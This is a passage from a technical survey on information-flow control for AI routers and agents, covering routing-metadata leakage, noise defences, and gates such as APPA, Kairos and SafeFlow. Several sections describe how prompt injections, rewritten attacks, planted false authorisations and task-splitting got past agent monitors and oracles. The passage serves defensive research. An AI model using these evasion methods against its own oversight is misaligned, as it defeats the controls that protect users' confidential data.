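Counting the possible outcomes limits this leak, as it did for the assistant's fixed messages to Dev. A decision with m possible outcomes has a min-entropy leakage of at most log₂ m bits, so after k decisions the limit is

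$$k \log_2 m$$

*ComplianceGate* sends each query to one of four endpoints, so an observer who sees which endpoint was used learns at most two bits per query. Over 20 queries the limit is 40 bits, and 33 bits are enough to give everyone on Earth a different number. If the observer can also tell fast answers from slow ones, each query may have eight possible outcomes, which would raise the limit for 20 queries to 60 bits.

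The actual leak is usually much smaller. Suppose 10% of queries are confidential, the classifier is perfect, and the observer sees only whether each query stayed local. Each decision then reveals 0.47 bits on average. But as with the access keys, the average is misleading, because whenever a query stays local, the observer knows for certain that it is confidential.

Garby and colleagues use the same count to limit an attacker's influence. If an agent reads a stranger's email and picks one of n fixed categories for the subject line of its reply, the stranger can affect at most log₂ n bits of that subject line. This limit has not yet been formally proved for their construction.

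### Labels with labels of their own

Zheng and Myers studied labels that a program discovers only while it runs, such as the permissions on a file. In their language, a label is a value like any other, so it has a label of its own. A program can test whether one label may flow to another, and this test can leak. Here is a simplified version of one of their examples, in which x is a label and the choice of label is itself secret:

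```
if x may flow to public: m1 = 0
else: m2 = 0
```

Anyone who can read `m1` and `m2` learns something about x from which of them changed. To prevent this, the type checker raises pc after a label test. If the two labels in the test have labels ℓ₁′ and ℓ₂′ of their own, both branches run with the program-counter label

$$pc \sqcup \ell_1' \sqcup \ell_2'$$

Zheng and Myers use this rule and their others to prove noninterference for every program that passes the type checker. The proof doesn't cover leaks through timing or through programs that never finish.

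By the same rule, the router's verdict on the merger memo should have the label {Ana, Ben}, because the classifier computed it from the memo. Using that verdict to choose a destination then raises pc to {Ana, Ben}. The cloud provider can see requests sent to it, so the type checker would reject the router, however accurate its classifier was.

LLMbda is similarly strict. A program can compute a label at run time, but it can only add that label to the ones a value already has. The value also takes on the label of any data used to compute the new label. If a classifier reads the memo and answers "public", the memo is still labelled {Ana, Ben}.

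If Ana pastes the text in without its label, both systems treat it as public. They let the router classify the text and act on the result, but their theorems then protect neither the text nor the result. Strict information flow control therefore forbids routing the text by its content only if the text still has the right label. A company that wants such a router has to treat each visible decision as a small declassification and decide how many to allow.

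### What routing records reveal about real users

*Sensitive-Topic Leakage Through LLM Routing Metadata*, from October 2026, measures how much somebody could learn from routers' choices without reading the requests. The researcher ran 1.7 million real requests from two public collections of chatbot conversations through several routers.

Many companies keep records that would allow this. Their requests usually pass through a gateway, a program that forwards each request to a model and tracks usage. The study surveyed 11 gateways, routers and cloud platforms. At least six of them (OpenRouter, LiteLLM, Kong, Cloudflare, Helicone and AWS) can record the caller and the model for each request while content logging is off. OpenRouter and LiteLLM do this by default, as does AWS for the most common calls to its Bedrock service. In an organisation that uses OpenRouter, every member can see which models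 handled the other members' requests.

Companies need these records for billing and monitoring, so the study doesn't treat them as a security flaw. The danger is that once content logging is off, employees may believe nobody can tell what they ask about.

RouteLLM, one of the main routers in the study, predicts whether an expensive model would give a better answer than a cheap one and routes by cost and quality. It does not assess how sensitive a request is. The researcher set it to send half of the ordinary requests to the expensive model. It sent only 19% of medical requests there, 33 percentage points below the rate for ordinary requests of similar length.

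Routing decisions also revealed information about other topics. On prompts outside the exploratory data, RouteLLM sent requests involving harassment or self-harm to the expensive model 19 percentage points less often than comparable requests. It sent sexual requests to that model 10 points more often. Another cost-and-quality router, notdiamond-0001, sent sexual requests to the expensive model less often, so an observer has to know how a particular router behaves to infer the topic from its choice.

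The study measures how well such decisions separate two groups by the area under the receiver operating characteristic curve, or AUC. This is the chance that a random member of one group gets a higher score than a random member of the other, counting ties as half. Guessing gives 0.5 and perfect separation gives 1. For a single decision, if the expensive model receives a share p of one group's requests and a share q of the other's, then

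$$\mathrm{AUC} = \frac{1}{2} + \frac{|p - q|}{2}$$

With 19.2% of medical requests and 50% of ordinary ones, the AUC is about 0.65, so one decision says little about one request.

A series of routing decisions reveals more about a person than a single decision. The researcher compared users who asked medical questions at least 20% of the time with users who never did, and counted how many of each user's first 20 requests RouteLLM sent to the expensive model. This count separated the two groups with an AUC of 0.71, compared with 0.54 for the length of the requests alone. Counting the requests labelled as health by a domain router, which classifies requests by subject, gave an AUC of 0.92.

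RouteLLM's 0.71 is below the 0.75 target that the researcher set in advance. A language model labeled which requests were medical, and its labels failed an accuracy check, so all the medical results are exploratory. The 0.92 is also an upper estimate, because the domain router's own labels helped select the messages that this language model was given.

An AUC of 0.71 is too low to identify individuals reliably. The test included about 16 users with no medical requests for every frequent asker, so a list of the highest-scoring users would probably be mostly people who had never made one. An employer could still use such a list to decide whom to watch.

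A router that keeps sensitive requests local resembles the domain router more than RouteLLM, because its decision is itself sensitive information. The study did not test such a router.

### Defences and their costs

The researcher tested several ways of changing RouteLLM's decisions to hide medical requests. The two AUC columns in the table use each user's first 20 requests. One is for an observer who knows only how many requests went to the expensive model, as on a bill, and the other is for an observer with the full log. "Benefit kept" is the router's own estimate of how much better it still does than random routing.

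| Defence | Benefit kept | Medical gap, in points | AUC from the count | AUC from the full log |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 33 | 0.72 | 0.74 |
| Replace half of the decisions with coin flips | 50% | 16 | 0.69 | 0.71 |
| Keep one model for each conversation | 81% | 32 | 0.69 | 0.70 |
| Keep one model for each user | 60% | 20 | 0.60 | 0.59 |
| Equalise rates between topics, using a cheap classifier | 99% | 15 | 0.65 | 0.66 |
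| Equalise rates between topics, using perfect labels | 99% | 0 | 0.60 | 0.61 |
| Send exactly half of each user's requests to each model | 23% | 5 | 0.50 | 0.73 |

Equalising routing rates works best for individual requests. For each topic and length, the system sends the same share of requests to the expensive model, choosing those that the router scores highest. On a benchmark with known answers and prices, this changed accuracy by at most 0.2 percentage points. But the system has to recognise medical requests to hide them, and with a lightweight classifier, more than 40% of the gap in routing rates remained.

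The defence in the last row works against one observer but not another. The router chooses a model for the first request in each pair, and the second request goes to the other model. After an even number of requests, each model has received exactly half, so a bill reveals nothing. But the full log still contains the router's choices in the odd positions. An attack that used only those positions reached 0.73, nearly as high as with no defence.

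The "benefit kept" column deserves only limited weight. On the same benchmark, RouteLLM was 1.3 points less accurate than random routing that sent the same share of requests to the expensive model. Its decisions revealed something about the topic of the requests without improving the answers. A company might therefore lose little by giving up such a router, though the benchmark's questions differ from ordinary chats.

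A router meant to protect confidential text can't do so by sending the same share of confidential and harmless requests to the cloud. That would hide the label, but it would also send confidential requests to the cloud.

### Adding noise to the route

Gaikwad (2025), in *AVEC*, proposes to randomise the record of whether a device answered a query itself or passed it to a remote model. The method is the one PRISM uses to replace entities, but with only two possible values, so with a privacy budget ε the record is true with probability e^ε/(1 + e^ε). Gaikwad shows that an observer's advantage is then at most

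$$\frac{e^{\varepsilon} - 1}{e^{\varepsilon} + 1} = \tanh\left(\frac{\varepsilon}{2}\right)$$

Advantage here ranges from 0 (guessing) to 1 (certainty). With ε = 1, the record is true 73% of the time and the advantage is at most 0.46. With ε = 0.1, the record is true 52.5% of the time and the advantage is at most 0.05.

Repeated queries weaken this protection. If 20 queries all reflect the same fact about a person, simply adding their budgets of 0.1 each gives a total of 2, which raises the limit on the advantage to 0.76. *AVEC* adds up budgets more precisely, but the total still grows with every query.

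Gaikwad also proves that some randomness is necessary. If a router always makes the same decision for the same text, and changing one name would change that decision, then a particular route has probability 1 with one name and 0 with the other. No finite privacy budget allows this. PRISM has this problem because it always takes the most probable route, a choice that its privacy theorem does not cover.

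Adding noise only to the record doesn't stop the company running the remote model from knowing which queries it received. Adding noise to the route itself, with ε = 1, sends 27% of the queries that should stay local to the remote model. *AVEC* reduces the harm by disguising the sensitive names and numbers it finds in those queries, as PRISM does. Gaikwad tested the design only in simulation and measured costs, delays and how often queries left the device, but not how well an observer could guess the secret.

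Ana's company could add noise only in the safe direction, by keeping some harmless requests local at random. Suppose 1,000 of its 10,000 daily requests are confidential and the router identifies them perfectly. If 20% of the 9,000 harmless requests also stay local, the local model handles 1,800 extra requests a day, for a total of 2,800. The chance that an observer who picks a local request finds a confidential one falls from 100% to 36%. But this does little to hide a long run of confidential requests. A colleague who sends 20 harmless requests would expect about four to stay local, so if all 20 of Ana's do, the technician will still notice.

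## Limiting what a wrong judgement can release

Any classifier will sometimes be wrong, but system designers can limit what its errors release. For example, Ana's company could ignore the classifier's output whenever it would widen access to the merger memo, or use the classifier only for decisions about recipients inside the company.

### Labels that a classifier can only raise

The simplest design keeps the provenance label and lets the classifier add restrictions to it. If p is the provenance label and c is the content label, the data gets the label p ⊔ c. The gate sends it to a destination d only if p ⊔ c ⊑ label(d). Since a join is at least as restrictive as each of its parts,

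$$p \sqsubseteq p \sqcup c \sqsubseteq \mathrm{label}(d)$$

The gate therefore permits only releases that the provenance label alone would have permitted. This holds for any c, even if the classifier guesses at random or an attacker controls it, as long as p is correct and the system carries p through every rewrite.

The merger memo has the provenance label {Ana, Ben}. If the classifier labels it "everyone", the intersection of the two labels is still {Ana, Ben}. If the classifier labels it {Ana}, Ben can't receive his summary. Apart from what a refusal reveals, wrongly blocking a reader in this way is the only harm the classifier can cause with the memo.

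Labels with several parts work the same way. *Agenra* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) describes a policy language for agents in which a label records a sensitivity level, a set of categories and whether the source is trusted. Joining two labels keeps the higher level and every category from either one, and the result counts as trusted only if both sources were.

Agenra takes its labels from registered sources, but a company could use the same join to combine such labels with a classifier's. Suppose a file is confidential by provenance and has no categories. A classifier wrongly labels it public but finds a password in it. The join keeps the file confidential despite the wrong label and adds the category for credentials.

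The classifier is most useful when the provenance label is too weak, as with pasted text. It catches confidential pastes that the label alone would miss, but no theorem covers the ones it misses, and an attacker who chose the wording might get more past it.

False alarms are the price. If the classifier flags 2% of the 9,000 harmless queries that Ana's company handles each day, 180 of them stay local unnecessarily. The cost can be higher for an agent, because joins spread a false alarm to everything the agent writes afterwards. If an agent reads 30 public documents, each with an independent 2% chance of a false alarm, the chance that at least one restricts its context is

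$$1 - 0.98^{30} \approx 45\%$$

An outsider could also deliberately cause over-blocking by sending the agent an email full of words such as "confidential" and "merger". The classifier cannot lower a label, so a person has to correct its false alarms.

### Unknown labels with a preset limit

Many tools supply no provenance label. *APPA* treats such a label as unknown instead of guessing a default. Its agent keeps a label L, the join of all known labels, and a list of the sources whose labels are missing. Unlabelled text can pass through summaries and other intermediate steps without stopping the work.

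When a check needs a label that the text lacks, for instance because the assistant is trying to email it, the system calls a registered component called a cast, which can be a classifier. An administrator has already set the least restrictive label that each cast may return. The system blocks the email if there is no suitable cast, or if the cast fails or returns a label less restrictive than its limit.

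Suppose a new search tool returns the merger memo without a label, and the cast's limit is "all staff". If the cast returns {Ana, Ben}, the assistant can send Ben a summary. If it returns "everyone", the answer exceeds the limit and the system blocks the email. If it returns "all staff", the summary can go to Dev, which is a leak, but not to a competitor.

*APPA* puts more restrictive labels lower in its ordering. Turned round to match Denning's, its "no-laundering" proposition has two parts. Let mᵢ be the limit on the i-th cast and λᵢ the label that the cast returns. The system accepts λᵢ only if mᵢ ⊑ λᵢ, and then joins it to L. After k casts,

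$$L \sqcup m_1 \sqcup \dots \sqcup m_k \;\sqsubseteq\; L \sqcup \lambda_1 \sqcup \dots \sqcup \lambda_k = L_{\text{final}}$$

This holds for any cast, even a malicious one, because ordinary code checks the limits. The other part needs an assumption. Let uᵢ be the label that a complete and correct annotation would have given the i-th source. A cast is sound if uᵢ ⊑ λᵢ, meaning that it never returns a label that is too permissive. If every cast is sound and the gate permits a release to d, then

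$$L \sqcup u_1 \sqcup \dots \sqcup u_k \;\sqsubseteq\; L_{\text{final}} \;\sqsubseteq\; \mathrm{label}(d)$$

so the release would also have passed with correct labels throughout.

Nobody can show that a learned cast is sound, because soundness must hold for every text the cast might receive, and even a test with no misses only puts an upper bound on the miss rate. *APPA* acknowledges that an unsound cast can allow a release that correct labels would have stopped.

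The limit is then the only firm protection, and it is only as good as the administrator's knowledge. A limit of {Ana, Ben} would protect the memo completely, but to set it the administrator would have to know who may read the memo, which the cast was supposed to determine. A limit of "everyone" would allow any mistake. A realistic limit is a coarse provenance label, such as "nothing from this tool leaves the company", and the cast adds finer restrictions to it.

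The researchers tested APPA on two benchmarks. AgentThreatBench has 24 tasks based on known types of attack on agents, and Bench-Corp has 20 office tasks that the researchers wrote. In one Bench-Corp task, a user asks an agent to combine project codes from two merger files, one from HR and one from finance, and send the result to the chief financial officer and the controller. Only the chief financial officer may read both files, so the policy should block the copy to the controller.

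The experiments covered 6,600 runs on three models, including comparisons with other set-ups. No attack succeeded in the 1,320 runs with APPA's protections on, and the agents completed 64.2% to 91% of their tasks, depending on the model, benchmark and prompt. In Bench-Corp runs without enforcement, attacks succeeded 30.0% to 39.5% of the time, so harmless attacks don't explain the lack of successes with protections on.

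After a refusal, APPA lists the permitted ways forward, such as asking for approval or reading a risky document in a separate branch of the conversation. Without these lists, one model's completion rate on Bench-Corp fell from 88% to 35%, and there were still no successful attacks.

The 1,320 runs repeat only 44 tasks. If all runs of a task had the same outcome, the result would be compatible with attacks succeeding on up to about 7% of similar tasks. It also provides little evidence about casts, because the researchers measured the whole system and did not report how often a cast returned the wrong label.

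### Approvers with limited authority

A system can also limit which releases a model can approve. *KAIROS* (Hempel, Loose and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that runs an agent inside a virtual machine and checks every file change and network request that leaves it. Under a written policy, the system refuses any action that a rule forbids. It releases any other action if the values that steer it, such as the recipient's address, come from a trusted source and the recipient is allowed to have the data. It defers everything else to an "oracle", which can be a person but was a language model in the tests.

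The agent can often continue while an action waits. Kairos applies file changes to a private copy and gives the agent a placeholder reply to a held message. The oracle can then consider what the agent did next, which may show whether an innocent-looking step began an attack. If the system can't interpret the oracle's answer, it refuses the action.

Let V be the set of actions that the policy releases by itself and D the set that it defers. Whatever the oracle answers, the set R of actions that go ahead satisfies

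$$V \subseteq R \subseteq V \cup D$$

The oracle therefore can't release anything that a rule forbids. Ana's company could forbid all email to outside addresses while the assistant works on the merger. If the assistant drafted an email to Dev containing the signing date, and Kairos recognised the date as confidential, the oracle would decide. A wrong approval would give Dev the date, but the oracle could never approve an email to a competitor.

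On AgentDojo, with GPT-4.1 as the agent, Kairos reduced successful attacks from 47.0% to 2.7%. When there was no attack, the agent completed 85.1% of tasks with Kairos, about the same as the 82.7% it completed undefended. When the researchers refused every deferred action instead of sending it to the oracle, completion fell to 42.7% and the attack rate barely changed. So in these tests the security came from the policy, and the oracle mainly let more tasks finish. The policy released 83% of actions by itself in the runs without attacks, and the oracle approved all but one of the actions it judged.

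But the researchers wrote no forbidding rules for these tests, because such rules would have built knowledge of the attacks into the policy. The oracle could release anything that reached it, so the tests measured its judgement, not the effect of limiting what it could release. When an attacker rewrote each injection over six rounds, 8.8% of attacks succeeded, compared with 52.4% without a defence. The successful attacks targeted tasks in which the user tells the agent to follow a document. They worked because the oracle treated the document's instructions as the user's own.

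The policy can also miss confidential data from the memo, because Kairos recognises such data by searching outgoing text for words from sensitive files. An email that mentions Oslo would match the memo, but one about "the Norwegian capital" might not, and the policy could then release it to Dev without consulting the oracle. Hempel and colleagues guarantee that every action passes through the monitor and that no refused action takes effect, but they can only measure whether the monitor releases the right actions.

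*APPA* gives each approver a mandate that limits what it can approve. For example, a mandate might let a model approve releasing merger data to Dev and nobody else. Code enforces the mandate, so even an attacker who controls everything the agent reads can't get approval to release the data to a competitor. By contrast, the isolated checker in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* can approve a message to any unknown recipient.

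Each approval in APPA also covers one exact message and leaves the memo's label unchanged, so the next email to Dev needs a new approval. Shivakumar and colleagues apply a similar rule, under which an approval is used up even if the mail server rejects the message, and the agent must get another before it tries again. Single-use approvals limit the damage from one mistake, but an approver who handles 20 requests can make a mistake on any of them.

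### Models that only supply evidence

*SafeFlow* (Dai, Ying and colleagues, 2026) gives its model no power to approve anything. The system monitors a group of agents that pass work to one another. The model reads the user's request and the messages between agents, and attaches labels from a fixed list, such as "sensitive read" and "external send", along with the words that support each one. A pattern matcher and a set of rules about tools also add labels. When these sources disagree, SafeFlow keeps all their labels, which is a raise-only rule.

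SafeFlow holds actions that can't be undone until it has a record of the whole task. It then uses fixed rules to search this record for forbidden paths, such as one from a sensitive file to an outside address. The model can identify evidence, but its explanations can't remove a label or authorise a release.

Suppose one agent reads the merger memo, a second turns it into a note about a trip to Oslo, and a third puts the note in a draft email to an outside travel agent. If the memo was labelled "sensitive read" at the first step, the label follows the text and the rules block the email, even if the model rates the note harmless. If the memo never got that label, the rules don't treat the email's path as forbidden. The task must still need the email and the recipient must be authorised, but the email may meet both conditions.

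A model that cannot approve a release can therefore still cause one by overlooking something, and Dai and colleagues list missed labels among SafeFlow's failures. The system could prevent this by including the memo's provenance label among the labels it combines, because the model could not then remove that label by overlooking something.

On four benchmarks of attacks and harmful requests, SafeFlow reduced the success rate from 69.3% to 12.7% (56 of 440 cases). The rate rose to between 20.9% and 24.5% when attackers tried to hide the evidence, for example by splitting a task between agents. Planting a false authorisation in text that the model read raised it less, to 15.4%. The small increase fits a design in which the model can't authorise anything, though the planted text could still distract it from the evidence. The benchmarks include unsafe code and harmful web tasks as well as disclosures,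 so these figures are not miss rates for confidential data.

When the researchers increased the number of labels from seven to 14, successful attacks fell from 12.7% to 8.9%, but false alarms rose from 5.9% to 7.4%, as they usually do when restrictions are added.

### Drafts that a person approves

Thornton and colleagues found that models often got recipient lists wrong. They suggested that a model draft the descriptive labels and an accountable person check the recipient list before a fixed gate enforces it, but they left testing this to future work. How well it works will depend on how many drafts need correcting and how many of the mistakes the reviewer notices.

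If a model's draft wrongly lists Carla among the merger memo's readers, Ana can correct it in seconds, but a records clerk who has only the text can't. The reviewer therefore has to know who may read the memo, and has to read the draft before approving it. If Ana approves it without looking, the gate will let Carla read the memo.

*Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026) gives some idea of how much work it takes to label tools. Three people independently labelled 538 tools from their descriptions. A model's labels matched the human consensus for 95.8% of the tools on the main action and 85.7% on data sensitivity. A reviewer starting from the model's labels would have had to correct about 77 sensitivity labels, and to check all 538 to find them, because nothing marks the wrong ones. A reviewer who missed one in five of these errors would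 leave about 15 wrong labels in use.

Ji and colleagues concluded from their test of 80 tools that people could adopt most of a model's labels after a review and minor corrections. That is plausible for tools because one label covers every later use, although the researchers measured agreement rather than reviewing time. Documents would take much more work to review. At a minute each, 20,000 documents would take 333 hours, or about eight working weeks, and people write new ones every day.

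A human reviewer has less work if they only have to approve drafts that widen access. If every new document starts with its author as the only reader, a draft that adds no readers can't release anything, so it can take effect at once. The reviewer can then focus on the mistakes that are hardest to notice later, since a colleague who can't open a document will probably complain, but a document read by the wrong person may go unnoticed.

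A reviewer's approval doesn't make a label correct. Shivakumar and colleagues state that their monitor checks whether an approval exists and uses it only once, but doesn't check whether the reviewer judged correctly. The monitor therefore guarantees that a person accepted responsibility for the decision.

### How the roles compare

The guarantees in the table assume that every route out of the system passes through the gate.

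| Role given to the model | Effect of a miss | Effect of an over-block | Guarantee that survives |
|---|---|---|---|
| Adds restrictions to a provenance label | Data has only its provenance label, so the pasted memo can leave | Permitted data stays inside, and so does text derived from it | The gate releases nothing that the provenance label forbids |
| Resolves an unknown label within a limit (APPA) | Data can reach anyone the limit allows, such as Dev | The system holds harmless data | No unlabelled data goes beyond the limit |
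| Decides deferred actions (Kairos) | A wrong action goes ahead, such as an email to Dev with the signing date | The agent loses a useful action and may fail its task | No action that a rule forbids goes ahead |
| Supplies evidence to fixed rules (SafeFlow) | The rules may find no forbidden path and release the text | The system blocks a harmless action | The model can't remove a label or authorise a release |
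| Drafts labels for a person to approve | The wrong reader gets access if the reviewer overlooks the mistake | A permitted reader has to ask for access | No draft that adds readers takes effect without a person's approval |
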